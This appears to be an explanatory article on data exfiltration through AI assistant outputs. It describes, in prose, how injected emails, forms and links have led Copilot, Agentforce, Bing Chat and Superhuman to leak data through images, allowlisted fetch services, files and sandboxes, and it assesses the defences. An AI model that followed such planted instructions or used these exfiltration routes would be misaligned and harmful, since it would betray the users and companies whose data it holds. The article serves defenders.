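# Preventing data exfiltration through chatbot outputs: restricting links, recipients and encoded content

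## How a chatbot's answer can carry data out, and where it can be stopped

Data exfiltration is the unauthorized transfer of data from a system to someone outside it. The term predates chatbots, and security engineers also use it when an employee copies a client list to a memory stick or malware uploads files. Since 2023, researchers have reported a newer form in many assistants built on large language models, the text-generating programs behind ChatGPT and Microsoft Copilot. The assistant has permission to read private data. Someone without that permission gets the assistant to read a piece of text, and the assistant's output then carries the data out.

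Nobody has found a way to make a model immune to such text, so most defences restrict what the assistant can send and where.

### From a customer's message to a stranger's server

At a mail-order company, for example, an employee works through a queue of customer messages in a browser, with a support assistant in a panel beside the queue. The assistant is allowed to read the incoming messages and the customer records, which contain names, home addresses, phone numbers and past orders. A session is one user's conversation with the assistant, together with the data the assistant is allowed to read for it.

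An attacker needs no password to reach this session, only the company's contact form. The attack goes like this:

1. The attacker sends a complaint about a late parcel. Under the complaint, in white letters on a white background, is a second paragraph addressed to any AI assistant that reads it. It asks for a customer's details at the end of a certain web address.
2. The employee asks the assistant to summarize the new messages.
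3. The company's software joins the employee's request, the messages and the relevant records into one long text and passes it to the model.
4. The model follows the hidden paragraph as well as the employee's request. It writes an ordinary summary and, below it, an image whose address contains a customer's name and phone number.
5. The panel displays the answer. To show the image, the employee's browser requests it from that address.
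6. The attacker's server receives the request and records the address in its log, where the attacker reads the name and the number.

The last step works because of how a web address, or URL, is built. In `help.example/orders/status?number=5512`, the domain `help.example` determines which server gets the request. The path, `/orders/status`, identifies a page on that server, and the query string, the part after the question mark, carries extra values. Whoever runs the domain receives both the path and the query string, which can contain any text. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, so the attacker does not need special software. An attacker can also put data in the path or in a subdomain, a label placed in front of the domain.

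Step 5 depends on Markdown, a plain-text notation that many chat products use to format answers. In Markdown, a label in square brackets followed by an address in parentheses becomes a link, and adding an exclamation mark in front makes it an image. A browser opens a link only when somebody clicks it, but fetches an image as soon as it draws the page. This makes the image version of the attack zero-click, meaning that it works without the victim clicking or approving anything. The image can also be too small to notice. The programmer Simon Willison (2023) reported that Roman Samoilenko's demonstration of the technique on ChatGPT in April 2023 used a single-pixel image.

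Images and links are two of the four ways for data to get out that Microsoft (2025) lists in an account of its own defences. The third is the tool call. If the support assistant has a tool for opening web pages, it can load the attacker's address itself, and the request then comes from the company's server instead of the employee's browser. Browser rules do not govern this kind of request, called a server-side fetch. If the assistant can send email, it can send the data directly to the attacker. The fourth is covert channels, which pass information through something not meant to carry it. For example, if an outsider can observe whether the assistant used a certain tool, an injected instruction can make the tool's use depend on a fact in the customer's record, and the outsider learns the fact without receiving any text.

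### Why the model follows the hidden paragraph

The attack in the support queue is a prompt injection, which is text that the assistant reads as data, such as an email or web page, but obeys as an instruction. Willison coined the term in 2022 by analogy with SQL injection, in which somebody types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) described indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker never talks to the assistant but plants the text somewhere the assistant will later read it. The paper demonstrated this on Microsoft's Bing Chat, where instructions on a web page affected the chatbot even when the person reading the page couldn't see them.

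Programmers fixed SQL injection by sending commands and data to the database separately, so that it never runs the data as a command. A language model has no such separation, because it receives the employee's request and the attacker's paragraph as one sequence of text and predicts what comes next. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fixed as completely as SQL injection was. He recommends safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do. He considers searching incoming messages for suspicious phrases a poor substitute, because an attacker can reword the same instruction endlessly.

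Newer attacks hardly look like commands. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that outside researchers used against ChatGPT in 2025. The email reads like a routine note about a company restructuring, with a passing mention that the reader's assistant is authorized to submit an employee's name and address to a compliance system. The attack worked half the time in testing. OpenAI compares the assistant to a human customer service agent who can issue refunds. The employer expects some callers to mislead the agent, so it caps the refunds.

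*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) attributes the danger to a combination of three capabilities: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some way to communicate with the outside. Removing any one of them stops this kind of theft. The mail-order company's support assistant needs the first two, because it has to read incoming messages and look up records to answer questions about orders. The company can therefore only remove outside communication, which Willison considers generally the easiest of the three to remove. Vendors have usually done the same when somebody reported a leak.

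### The Bing Chat fix of 2023

In an early example, the security researcher Johann Rehberger found that text on a web page could take over Bing Chat while a user was chatting about that page. In his demonstration, described in *Bing Chat* on his blog Embrace The Red, the injected instruction made the chatbot wait two turns and then produce an image whose address contained a short summary of the page and the conversation, along with any passwords on the page. The summary was in base64, a standard encoding that uses letters, digits and a few symbols. When the browser loaded the image, it sent a secret from further down the page to Rehberger's server. An attacker would not have needed to own the page, since a reader's comment or an advertisement could have held the instruction.

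Rehberger reported the flaw to Microsoft on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft told him on June 15 that it had put a fix in place. His early 2026 Embrace The Red post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the fix to May 2023.

As far as he could tell from outside, at least part of the fix was a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule sent with a web page that limits which domains the browser may load images and other resources from. Bing's policy permitted images from four of Microsoft's own Bing domains. A list of permitted destinations that blocks everything else is called an allowlist. The model didn't have to recognize an attack, because the browser would not fetch the attacker's image even if the model followed the web page's instructions and wrote the image into its answer.

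Other companies fixed the same flaw at other points. Microsoft completed a fix for Azure AI Playground, a site for trying out models, in September 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, the software changed the text of the answer by putting a space between the brackets of the image notation, so the page no longer treated it as an image. Anthropic also fixed the flaw in Claude that year. Amazon went furthest with its business assistant, Amazon Q. Willison found by January 2024 that it had stopped producing links altogether. OpenAI at first declined to fix the problem in ChatGPT, but in December 2023 it began checking image addresses before displaying the images.

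### Three restrictions and the places to enforce them

These fixes all restrict links. For an assistant that can also send messages, a fuller set of restrictions would be:

- **No outside links.** Answers contain no address, whether of an image or a clickable link, on a domain the company has not approved.
- **No outside recipients.** The assistant sends email only to people who belong in the case, such as the customer whose record is open.
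- **No encoded content.** The assistant does not write text in forms that a person or a filter cannot readily read, such as base64 or invisible characters.

Restricting encoded content supports the restrictions on links and recipients. An approved link or a legitimate email can still carry a stranger's phone number, and software can find the number only if it is in a recognizable form.

Each restriction can be a sentence the model reads or a check that code performs, and there are six places to put it.

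| Place | What happens there in the support assistant | What upholds the rule |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt | The company's standing instructions forbid outside addresses | The model |
| Training | The developer trains the model to ignore instructions found in data | The model |
| Output filter | Software scans the finished answer and removes links or encoded strings | Code, or a second model |
| Screen | The browser or app refuses images from unapproved domains | Code |
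| Tool | The email tool rejects an unknown recipient; the web tool rejects an unknown address | Code |
| Network | A firewall blocks egress, traffic leaving the system for the outside network, except to approved domains | Code |

Microsoft calls a defence probabilistic if it makes an attack less likely to succeed, and deterministic if it guarantees that a particular attack fails, whatever the model does.

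*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) reports an experiment at eBay that compared several of these defences. The researchers gave a small open model, Qwen2.5 7B, a secret and a tool for making web requests, then asked it to summarize a page containing an injected instruction to send the secret away. They tested each defence in 30 runs. With no defence, the secret got out every time. A firm rule in the prompt against obeying web content reduced this to 66.7% of runs. Tags marking the web content as untrusted made no difference by themselves, and with both measures together the secret still got out in 56.7% of runs. With a domain allowlist, the model tried to send the secret in every run, but no request got out.

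The allowlist result is clear, because the model was fooled just as often and no data got out. But the test was easy, since the researchers deliberately chose an attacker's domain that no sensible allowlist would include. Their results for filters that inspect the content of a request are harder to interpret. Such filters are a simple form of data loss prevention (DLP), software that scans outgoing content for known kinds of sensitive data. Nothing leaked with a keyword filter on, but the model attempted a request in only 23.3% of those runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes disguised the secret, but a disguised secret should have passed the filter and reached the attacker, and none did. A filter that acts after the model has written its request should not change how often the model writes one, so the absence of leaks is weak evidence that the filter works.

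In 95% of the successful attacks in their larger set of 480 undefended runs, the answer on the screen was harmless and the secret went out only through the tool. A filter that checks the displayed answer but not the tool calls would have let nearly all of these attacks through.

Qwen2.5 7B is a weak model by 2026 standards, and training has made leading models much harder to fool. Anthropic reported in June 2026 that Claude Mythos 5 had the best result yet on a prompt injection benchmark run by the security company Gray Swan. OpenAI says that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the trained model refuses, and that a check in code handles the rest.

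The remaining risk depends on the setting and on how many times the attacker can try. According to Anthropic figures reported by VentureBeat, 200 injection attempts against Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, all failed in a constrained coding environment. When the model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without extra safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the success rate was 78.6% without the safeguards and 57.1% with them. A public contact form allows many attempts. Willison criticizes products that advertise catching 95% of attacks because an attacker can keep trying until one gets through.

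Code has a different weakness, which is that it enforces a rule exactly as written, and the rule may not cover what its author had in mind. Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a CSP that allowed images from Google's document domain. That was a poor choice of domain, because it also hosts Google Forms, which can store data sent in a web address. An injected email could therefore get the assistant to load an "image" whose address submitted the contents of other emails to the attacker's form, and the browser would correctly allow the request under the policy. Superhuman had fixed the problem by the time Willison recorded the case in January 2026.

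Redirects cause a similar problem. Many reputable sites forward visitors to other addresses, so a check of only the first domain can approve a request that ends up at the attacker's server. A CSP on images also doesn't restrict links that the employee clicks or pages that the company's server fetches.

Some products require human approval. Copilot in Outlook, for instance, drafts an email that the user has to approve and send. For the support desk, this would catch a message to an obvious stranger, but it would help less when the employee can't judge the address. OpenAI also warns that people who see frequent alerts learn to click through them.

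### How much a leak reveals

Suppose the company now forbids the model to write its own addresses and lets it open only pages that already exist. The model can still leak data through its choice of pages, a method Rehberger described in 2023. The attacker needs 36 existing pages, one for each letter and digit, on a site whose logs the attacker can read. The injected instruction tells the model to spell out the secret by opening the matching pages in order, so no single address contains anything private.

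In information theory, choosing one of N equally likely options reveals log₂ N bits, where a bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. Two options give 1 bit, four give 2, and each further doubling adds another. Choosing one of 36 equally likely characters reveals about 5.2 bits. If some options are more likely than others, the average is lower, so log₂ N is the most a choice can reveal on average.

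A ten-digit phone number holds at most about 33 bits. Spelling it out digit by digit takes ten page loads. An attacker who packs the digits more tightly could send it in seven loads with the same 36 pages, or in three with 4,096 pages, where each load carries 12 bits. By comparison, the Bing Chat attack could put a 200-character summary into one address, which would carry up to about 1,000 bits in a single request if the summary used only the same 36 characters. Restricting the assistant to existing pages therefore slows the leak enormously but doesn't stop it. Some secrets still fit in a single page load, such as whether a given person is a customer of the company, which is one bit.

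Ordinary browser behaviour makes it harder for an attacker to spell out data through page requests, using one page per character. Browsers keep copies of recently loaded pages, so a second request for the same page may never reach the server, and a repeated letter in a name can go missing. Requests can also arrive out of order. Embrace The Red suggests blocking repeat requests deliberately, by not letting an assistant open the same address twice in one session. The attacker would then need several pages for each character, which anyone with a large website probably has.

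## Microsoft 365 Copilot: removing links and blocking outside images

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the assistant that Microsoft sells to companies for use in Outlook, Word, Teams and its other office programs. When an employee asks a question, Copilot searches their mailbox, Teams chats, and files in OneDrive and SharePoint, Microsoft's services for storing and sharing documents. It then sends the question to a language model, along with whatever it found that seems relevant. Only people inside the company can use Copilot, but anyone can email them, so the model can receive a stranger's text together with text from confidential files.

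Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat relied at least partly on a list of permitted image domains. Copilot also has such a list, along with several other defenses. Researchers have published three attacks that got data out despite them: EchoLeak in June 2025, SearchLeak in June 2026 and ReLeak in December 2026. Microsoft fixed the flaws before publication in each case. In all three attacks, one of Microsoft's own servers sent the request that reached the attacker.

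### The layers between an email and the outside

Most of what outsiders know about Copilot's layers comes from the researchers who got past them. In the order in which an injected instruction would meet them, they are:

1. **Classifier for injected instructions.** Microsoft's name for indirect prompt injection is cross-prompt injection attack, or XPIA. A classifier, which is a model trained to sort text into categories, examines emails and other incoming text. It should stop injected instructions before they reach the model that writes the answer.
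2. **Removal of outside links.** Software deletes Markdown links and images from the answer if they lead outside the company's own pages.
3. **Neutralizing of HTML.** A model can also write an image in HTML, the language of web pages. Copilot's software wraps the answer in a code block, which makes the browser display the HTML as plain text instead of acting on it.
4. **CSP.** The browser loads images only from domains on Microsoft's allowlist.
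5. **Code sandbox.** Copilot can write and run Python code, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. The code runs in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that the system deletes afterwards. According to Microsoft's documentation, the machine allows no traffic in or out, and software scans the code for malicious patterns while it runs.

The link filter, the HTML wrapper and the CSP apply to the answer shown on the employee's screen. The sandbox stops programs running inside it from sending data over the network themselves. Copilot's chat also cannot submit web forms or send emails, according to a June 2026 news article reposted on SoylentNews. An attacker therefore has to find something else that will make a request.

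Microsoft sorts its defenses against prompt injection by purpose. To prevent injection, it uses carefully worded standing instructions and Spotlighting, which marks untrusted text so the model can distinguish it from the user's request. To detect injection, it uses a classifier called Prompt Shields. To limit the damage when an injection succeeds, it restricts who can see which data, asks users for consent, and deterministically blocks known exfiltration methods. Microsoft advises organizations that build their own AI systems to assume that indirect prompt injection is inevitable and to design those systems to contain it.

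The weak point in this account is the word "known". An attacker can look for a variant that the blocks don't cover.

### EchoLeak: a second link format and a Teams address

Aim Labs, the research arm of the security company Aim Security, found EchoLeak and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the CVE system, a public catalogue of software flaws. According to *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), the attacker sends one email to an employee. The employee doesn't have to open it, but does have to ask Copilot a question that leads it to retrieve the email.

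The team wanted Copilot to retrieve the email for as many questions as possible. Search systems of this kind commonly turn each passage of text into a vector, a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and pick the passages whose vectors are closest to the question's. A short email has only one vector and matches few questions. The team therefore wrote a long email, expecting the system to split it into passages. Each passage had a heading about a different office topic, such as onboarding or leave of absence, and repeated the same instructions. In the team's demonstration, Copilot retrieved the email when asked about various topics.

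The email got past the classifier because its instructions addressed the human recipient and never mentioned AI or Copilot, so they looked like an ordinary request from one person to another. Reddy and Gujral (2025), who analyze the published material in *EchoLeak*, expect that the classifier would have caught a cruder email telling Copilot to ignore its instructions. Ravia attributes the weakness to a lack of training data. Injections can be on any subject and in any tone or language, and good collections of real ones are scarce.

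The instructions directed the model to find the most sensitive item in its input and put it in a web address. That input could include the conversation so far and any emails or files Copilot had retrieved. Ravia calls this an LLM scope violation, meaning that text from outside the company directs a large language model to the company's internal data.

Copilot's link filter should have removed the resulting address, but it recognized only the common Markdown link format, in which the address comes right after the label. Markdown also has a reference format, which leaves the label in the sentence and puts the address on a separate line further down, like a footnote. The program that displayed the answer recognized both formats, so a reference link passed through the filter and appeared on the screen as a working link. Images in the reference format also passed through, and images don't need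 a click to load.

A gap like this can occur whenever a filter and a display program interpret text by different rules. A filter that searches for patterns has to recognize every notation the display program accepts. It would be safer to use the display program to identify the links in the answer, then remove them before anything reaches the screen.

The image now passed the filter, but the browser still blocked it because the attacker's domain was not on the allowlist. The list, which Ravia reproduces, has 29 distinct entries, nearly all for Microsoft services, compared with four domains in the Bing Chat policy of 2023. Several entries begin with an asterisk, which stands for any subdomain. The team searched the list for a service that would fetch an outside address on request.

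They first found one in SharePoint. Any customer can set up a SharePoint site, so an attacker can get a subdomain that the allowlist accepts. SharePoint also had a feature for embedding outside content, which made Microsoft's server fetch any address given in the request, but this worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The team then found a similar service in Teams, used for previews, that required no action from the victim.

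The finished attack used this Teams service. Copilot's answer contained an image with a Teams address, which had the attacker's address and the secret embedded in it. The browser loaded the image because the allowlist included Teams. The Teams server then requested the attacker's address, sending the secret to the attacker.

Copilot normally refers to the emails it has used, which could have revealed the attack. The injected text included a request that the recipient never mention the email, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot did not mention it.

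According to Reddy and Gujral's timeline, Microsoft began partial repairs in April 2025 and completed a fix on its own servers in May. The public disclosure followed on June 11. Customers did not have to install anything. Ravia believes that no setting available to a company's administrators could have prevented the attack. Microsoft said the attack had affected no customers.

### How an allowed domain undoes a CSP

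In EchoLeak, the browser complied with the CSP because it contacted only Teams. Teams' servers made the second request, which the CSP did not cover.

Data from the browser can reach every domain on the allowlist, plus any address that servers on those domains will fetch for anyone who asks. If even one of those servers will fetch any address, data can reach the entire public web, and the allowlist no longer limits where it can go. Teams had such a server, so cutting Copilot's allowlist from 29 entries to Teams alone would not have helped.

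A company's firewall would not have stopped the leak either, because the connection to the attacker started in Microsoft's data centre. The firewall could detect the employee's browser connecting to Teams, but that happens all day in a company that uses Microsoft's products.

Security engineers call this kind of flaw server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an outsider gets a server to make a request of the outsider's choosing. They usually worry about it because the server may be able to reach private systems that the outsider can't. But even a preview service that fetches only public web pages is dangerous when it is on the allowlist of an assistant that can write private data into addresses, and the people who maintain the service may not know it is on such a list.

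Reddy and Gujral tabulated how they expect eight defences to affect each step of an attack like EchoLeak. In the version below, "works" means they expect the defence to block the step, "fails" means they expect at least one way around it, and a dash means the defence does not apply.

| Defence | Scope violation | Classifier bypass | Link filter bypass | Automatic image loading | Allowed domain as proxy | Zero-click leak |
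|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tags separating outside text in the prompt | works | works | – | – | – | fails |
| Internal sources only, by default | works | – | works | – | – | fails |
| Only approved formats in the answer | works | works | works | fails | – | fails |
| List of allowed or banned addresses | – | – | works | fails | works | works |
| Strict CSP | – | – | – | works | works | works |
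| Signed image proxy | – | – | – | works | works | works |
| Human approval for outside content | works | works | works | works | – | works |
| Scanning of outgoing traffic | – | – | – | – | – | fails |

The table contains predictions. Reddy and Gujral ran no experiments, although one sentence of their paper refers to tests. The last column matters most because it covers whether data gets out without a click. Four of the eight defences are predicted to prevent this, and all four either restrict the request itself or have a person approve it. Defences that only change what the model reads, or check the format of what it writes, are predicted to fail.

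Some of the table's entries are doubtful. Using only internal sources by default relies on provenance, the record of where a piece of data came from. Reddy and Gujral predict in the table that this would fail to stop a zero-click leak, but elsewhere in the paper they write that EchoLeak could not work if Copilot never used email from unknown outsiders to answer questions about internal projects. The second judgement is more convincing, because the model cannot obey an email that it never receives. However, Copilot would also leave out relevant messages from new customers and suppliers unless the employee asked for them.

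The entry for a strict CSP is too optimistic. Reddy and Gujral recommend allowing only the company's own domains, without wildcards, but an allowlist that named the exact Teams server would follow this advice and still let EchoLeak through.

The signed image proxy addresses the Teams flaw more directly. This server fetches images for the browser, but only from addresses that have not expired and carry a valid signature, a code that only the company's own software can compute. An attacker can get the model to write any address, but neither of them can sign it. The protection fails if the software automatically signs every address in the model's answer.

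### SearchLeak: an image request sent before the check

A year after EchoLeak, a different Microsoft service on the allowlist let data out. *SearchLeak*, published by the data security company Varonis on June 15, 2026, describes an attack (CVE-2026-42824) that starts with a link instead of an email. The victim has to click the link once. Tools that block suspicious links let it through because it leads to a genuine Microsoft address.

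The link opened Copilot's enterprise search page with a query already filled in. Links to web search engines can also contain queries, but Copilot passed the query to its language model, which could follow it as an instruction. The attacker's text took the place of the employee's request. In the demonstration, it made Copilot look up an email and put the subject line in the address of an image. A subject line alone can be valuable because some services put login codes there.

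Varonis had the model write the image in HTML. The code block around the answer should have made this harmless, but the software added it only once the answer was complete. Copilot, like most chatbots, streams its answers, showing the text while the model is still writing it. The page therefore rendered the model's HTML as it arrived, and the browser requested the image as soon as the model had written the tag, before the code block turned the tag into plain text.

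This is a race condition, a flaw in which the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. The browser could act well before the wrapper, because it needed only the first complete tag while the wrapper waited for the end of the answer. Varonis recommends cleaning the text when the page displays it. For a streamed answer, the software would have to hold back each tag until it was complete and checked, which would slightly delay that part of the answer.

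The CSP still blocked images from the attacker's domain, but it allowed images from Bing. Bing has a search-by-image feature in which a user supplies a picture's address and Bing's server fetches the picture for analysis. SearchLeak's image pointed to this feature and supplied an address on the attacker's domain that contained the email title. When Bing's server requested that address, it sent the title to the attacker.

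Varonis points out that the attack needed every flaw it exploited. Copilot had two defenses against the image, and both had gaps. The browser would not have loaded the image if the code block had been in place earlier, and the CSP would have stopped the request if Bing had not fetched outside addresses.

The Bing gap was easier to foresee than the race. Ravia's 2025 copy of the allowlist already includes Bing, and EchoLeak had shown that attackers can get data out through an allowed service that fetches URLs. Checking the rest of the list for similar services would have been a natural next step, and Varonis now recommends this check to anyone who maintains a CSP.

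Microsoft fixed SearchLeak the week before Varonis published it. Varonis writes that Microsoft gave it a maximum severity rating of critical, while TechRadar reported a rating of "10/10 critical", which combines two different scales. Critical is the highest of Microsoft's own severity labels. A score out of ten comes from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which uses fixed criteria, including whether the victim has to do something. Under CVSS version 3.1, an attack that requires a click can score at most 9.6, so the ten is probably a misreading of Microsoft's label. STAR Labs' *M365 Copilot* (2026) lists another Copilot flaw, CVE-2026-24299, as critical even though its CVSS score is only 5.3.

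Varonis first used a link with a hidden instruction against the consumer version of Copilot in an attack called Reprompt. Copilot's check against leaks covered only the first request, so an instruction to make every request twice got around it. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* describes CoSnitch, a later Varonis attack on the same product. Whenever Copilot refused something, the researchers asked why, and its explanations helped them build a link that ran their instruction as soon as the victim clicked. If the victim had connected Gmail, Google Drive or a calendar, the instruction could reach those too. CoSnitch also used a flaw that let a web page plant instructions in Copilot's long-term memory when the user asked for a summary, and these remained even if the user changed passwords. Microsoft learned of CoSnitch (CVE-2026-24301)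 in December 2025, rated its severity 8.8 and has fixed it on its servers.

### ReLeak: an image, a document and a sandbox

Cato Networks, a network security company, bought Aim Security in September 2025, and the team that had found EchoLeak became part of Cato AI Labs. On December 3, 2026, Cato AI Labs published three new attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents all three as zero-click. As with EchoLeak, each began with an email that Copilot retrieved while working on an employee's normal request, and the classifier again failed to stop it. According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot did not carry out direct commands but followed instructions that looked like legitimate requests.

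The attacks differ in how the data left. Infosecurity Magazine gives the details and the dates of Microsoft's fixes, all in 2026.

| Where Copilot put the data | What sent it to the attacker | CVE number | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| The address of an image in the answer | Bing's servers | CVE-2026-124115 | November 15 |
| A link in a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file | Microsoft's background processing of files | CVE-2026-124132 | November 11 |
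| Python code in the sandbox | The code itself | CVE-2026-78501 | September 17 |

Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20, according to *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026). Microsoft therefore took between four and seven weeks to fix the sandbox, and roughly three months or more to fix each of the other two flaws. Cato did not demonstrate all three in a single attack, but each attack worked on its own, so fixing the sandbox in September left two ways to extract data until November.

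The image route resembled SearchLeak: the browser loaded an image through Bing, and Bing's server contacted the attacker. Cato reported it after Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak in June, so the fix evidently hadn't blocked every way of sending data out through Bing. ReLeak was also more dangerous than SearchLeak, because the instruction arrived by email and the victim didn't have to click anything.

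The attacker could use a file instead of the on-screen answer to extract data. The injected instruction made Copilot create a file containing a link with confidential data in its address. Copilot saved the file to OneDrive or SharePoint, where Microsoft's servers automatically processed it and requested the link. Antipov reports that in Cato's tests, the data left one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file.

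The CSP could not help because no browser was involved. A filter on the chat answer would also have missed the address, which was in the file. To cover this route, Microsoft would have to apply its link rules to every file Copilot writes or prevent the background service from contacting outside addresses. The second option is more reliable because it doesn't depend on finding every link format in four kinds of file.

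Cato found ways around the network restrictions on Copilot's code sandbox, and Python code running there sent confidential data straight to an outside server. Microsoft's documentation says that the sandbox allows no outbound traffic and that this prevents exfiltration. This is the only one of the three flaws with a public record, and Microsoft raised the flaw's CVSS score from 7.4 to 8.6. Companies can also use the code interpreter in agents they build with Copilot Studio, but Cato has not confirmed the flaw there.

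The sandbox's isolation had already failed at least once that year. Rubrik Zero Labs, the research group of a data security company, had built an attack called ChatMate, in which a malicious document made Copilot run code that broke out of the sandbox. The attacker could then type instructions to the victim's Copilot and read the replies. Head Topics' *RubrikがMicrosoft 365 Copilotの脆弱性と攻撃手法ChatMateを公開* reports that the victim in the demonstration saw only a harmless answer about the uploaded document.

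ChatMate began with CVE-2026-32193, a path traversal flaw in the Azure software that runs the sandbox. Such a flaw lets a file path lead a program outside its intended folder. The sandbox had no internet connection, but the machine underneath it did, so code that escaped could get online. If that machine had also lacked internet access, escaping the sandbox would not have been enough to send data out. Rubrik reported the flaw in February 2026, and Microsoft fixed it in April and paid a $48,000 reward.

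Cato's researchers found the ReLeak flaws by directing AI agents, which wrote test prompts, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. An attacker could automate the search in the same way, so it is risky for Microsoft to rely on an unusual link format or an obscure service going unnoticed.

Cato concludes that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. The company sells protection for AI systems, so it has an interest in that conclusion, and it knows of no customers harmed by ReLeak. But its findings support the criticism in one respect, because eighteen months after the EchoLeak disclosure, the same team published an attack in which Copilot obeyed a stranger's email and a Microsoft service on the allowlist delivered the data. The document and sandbox routes also rely on things Copilot can do besides answering questions, which neither a link filter nor a CSP on the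 chat page covers.

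## Salesforce Agentforce: a list of trusted domains with an expired entry

Salesforce sells customer relationship management (CRM) software, which companies use to keep records of customers and leads (potential customers). Agentforce is its platform for building AI agents that read those records, draft messages and take actions. Like Microsoft 365 Copilot, Agentforce displayed its answers on a page with a CSP. The attacks on Copilot needed a server on an allowed domain that would forward a request. The attack on Agentforce was simpler because one of the allowed domains had expired and was for sale.

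### ForcedLeak: a lead form and a lapsed domain

The Israeli startup Noma Security reported the flaw to Salesforce on July 28, 2025 and published it on September 25 under the name ForcedLeak. The Hacker News (2025) gives its CVSS score as 9.4 out of 10. The flaw affected companies that used Agentforce with Web-to-Lead, a feature that saves whatever visitors type into a form on the company's public website as new leads in the CRM.

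*Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025) quotes much of Noma's account. Noma's researchers first asked Agentforce general knowledge questions to see whether it would stray from Salesforce business, and it did. They then chose the form's description field because its high character limit left room for several instructions. They also had to guess how an employee would ask about a new lead, since the injected text would do nothing until the agent read it.

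Noma's final text was a short numbered list. It mixed trivial questions with a request for the leads' email addresses and ended by asking for an image with those addresses in its URL. When an employee asked about the lead, Agentforce looked up the email addresses and wrote the image in HTML. The employee's browser then requested the image from Noma's server, which logged the request.

The CSP should have blocked that request, but it permitted images from any subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`. That domain had gone back on sale after its registration lapsed, and Noma bought it. A CSP lists domains only by name, so the browser cannot detect that one has a new owner.

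Despite its name, the domain was separate from `salesforce.com`. If Salesforce had used a subdomain of `salesforce.com`, nobody could have bought it, because only a domain's owner can create names under it.

Customers were unlikely to notice the problem. Salesforce adds its own domains to the CSP, and its administrator guide, *Manage Trusted URLs*, explains that these are not among the trusted URLs defined in a customer's settings. The expired domain was probably one of these. To find it, an administrator would have had to read the CSP that Salesforce's server sent to the browser and look up who owned each domain in it.

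### A corrected CSP and a rule for the agent's output

Salesforce took the domain back and, as Willison recounts, audited and corrected the CSP. On September 8, 2025, it also began enforcing a rule called Trusted URLs on its agents' output. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that an administrator must approve every outside domain that an agent links to or calls. The company's own Salesforce addresses are allowed by default.

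The Trusted URLs rule applies to the agent's answer before the page displays it, whereas the CSP only controls what the browser loads for the page. The security company PromptArmor examined the rule in Agentforce's chat and reports in *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* that software replaces any unapproved address with the placeholder `[URL_REDACTED]`. This covers addresses in images, clickable links, HTML and CSS (the styling language of web pages, which can load a background picture). The rule also protects against phishing, since an injected "sign in again" link to an unapproved site loses its address.

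However, the two checks partly depend on the same list. When administrators add a trusted URL, they also choose what Salesforce pages may load from it, and an older version of Salesforce's guide describes images as selected by default. The approval applies to the whole organization as well as to its agents. An administrator who only wants an agent to link to a supplier's help pages may therefore also permit images from the supplier's domain. PromptArmor advises switching images off unless the company needs them. If the supplier later lets its domain expire, whoever buys it can receive data despite both checks. The new rule reduces the number of approved domains, but it doesn't detect when one of them has a new owner.

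The rule also doesn't cover everything an agent can do. Adversa AI's *Salesforce Agentforce Agent Security Risks* describes how an attack called PipeLeak got around Trusted URLs by sending data out by email. For actions the rule doesn't cover, Salesforce relies partly on human approval. In August 2025, according to its *Security Advisories*, the company began requiring confirmation before an agent used several standard actions, including cancelling an order, resetting a password and changing a customer's contact details.

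PromptArmor also recommends Salesforce's data masking, which replaces names, phone numbers and other sensitive details with placeholders before the text reaches the model. A model that never receives a phone number can't put it in a web address, whether in plain digits or encoded, but it also can't use the number for legitimate work.

### Superhuman: a Google domain where anyone can create a form

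Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* tells administrators to approve the domains of outside data sources, and gives `docs.google.com` as an example. Google is unlikely to lose that domain, but it also hosts Google Forms, where anyone can create a form and read the responses. Emails could leak from Superhuman this way because its CSP allowed images from the same domain.

Someone who creates a Google Form can also create a link that already contains the answers, and one version of this link submits the form as soon as a browser requests it. This is unusual because websites by convention store data only after a POST request, the kind that a submit button normally sends. Browsers load images with a GET request, which is meant for retrieving things. Google Forms stores answers from either kind of request, so a browser that loads such a link as an image submits the form,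 even though no picture comes back.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which the user asked for a summary of the last hour's mail. One message, which the user had not opened, presented a form as a way to give feedback on the search results. The assistant added text from the other messages to the form's web address, then used that as the address of an image in its answer. PromptArmor obtained the full text of several emails from one answer, including financial, legal and medical ones, and parts of more than 40 emails from another.

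Removing Google's domain from the CSP would not have prevented exfiltration, because Superhuman's assistant could also open web pages at any address to answer questions. An injected instruction could therefore send data directly to the attacker's site. A related product, Superhuman Go, displayed images from the attacker's domain. PromptArmor reported the first flaws on Friday evening, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features the following Monday, deployed a first patch the next day and continued patching until January 11, 2026.

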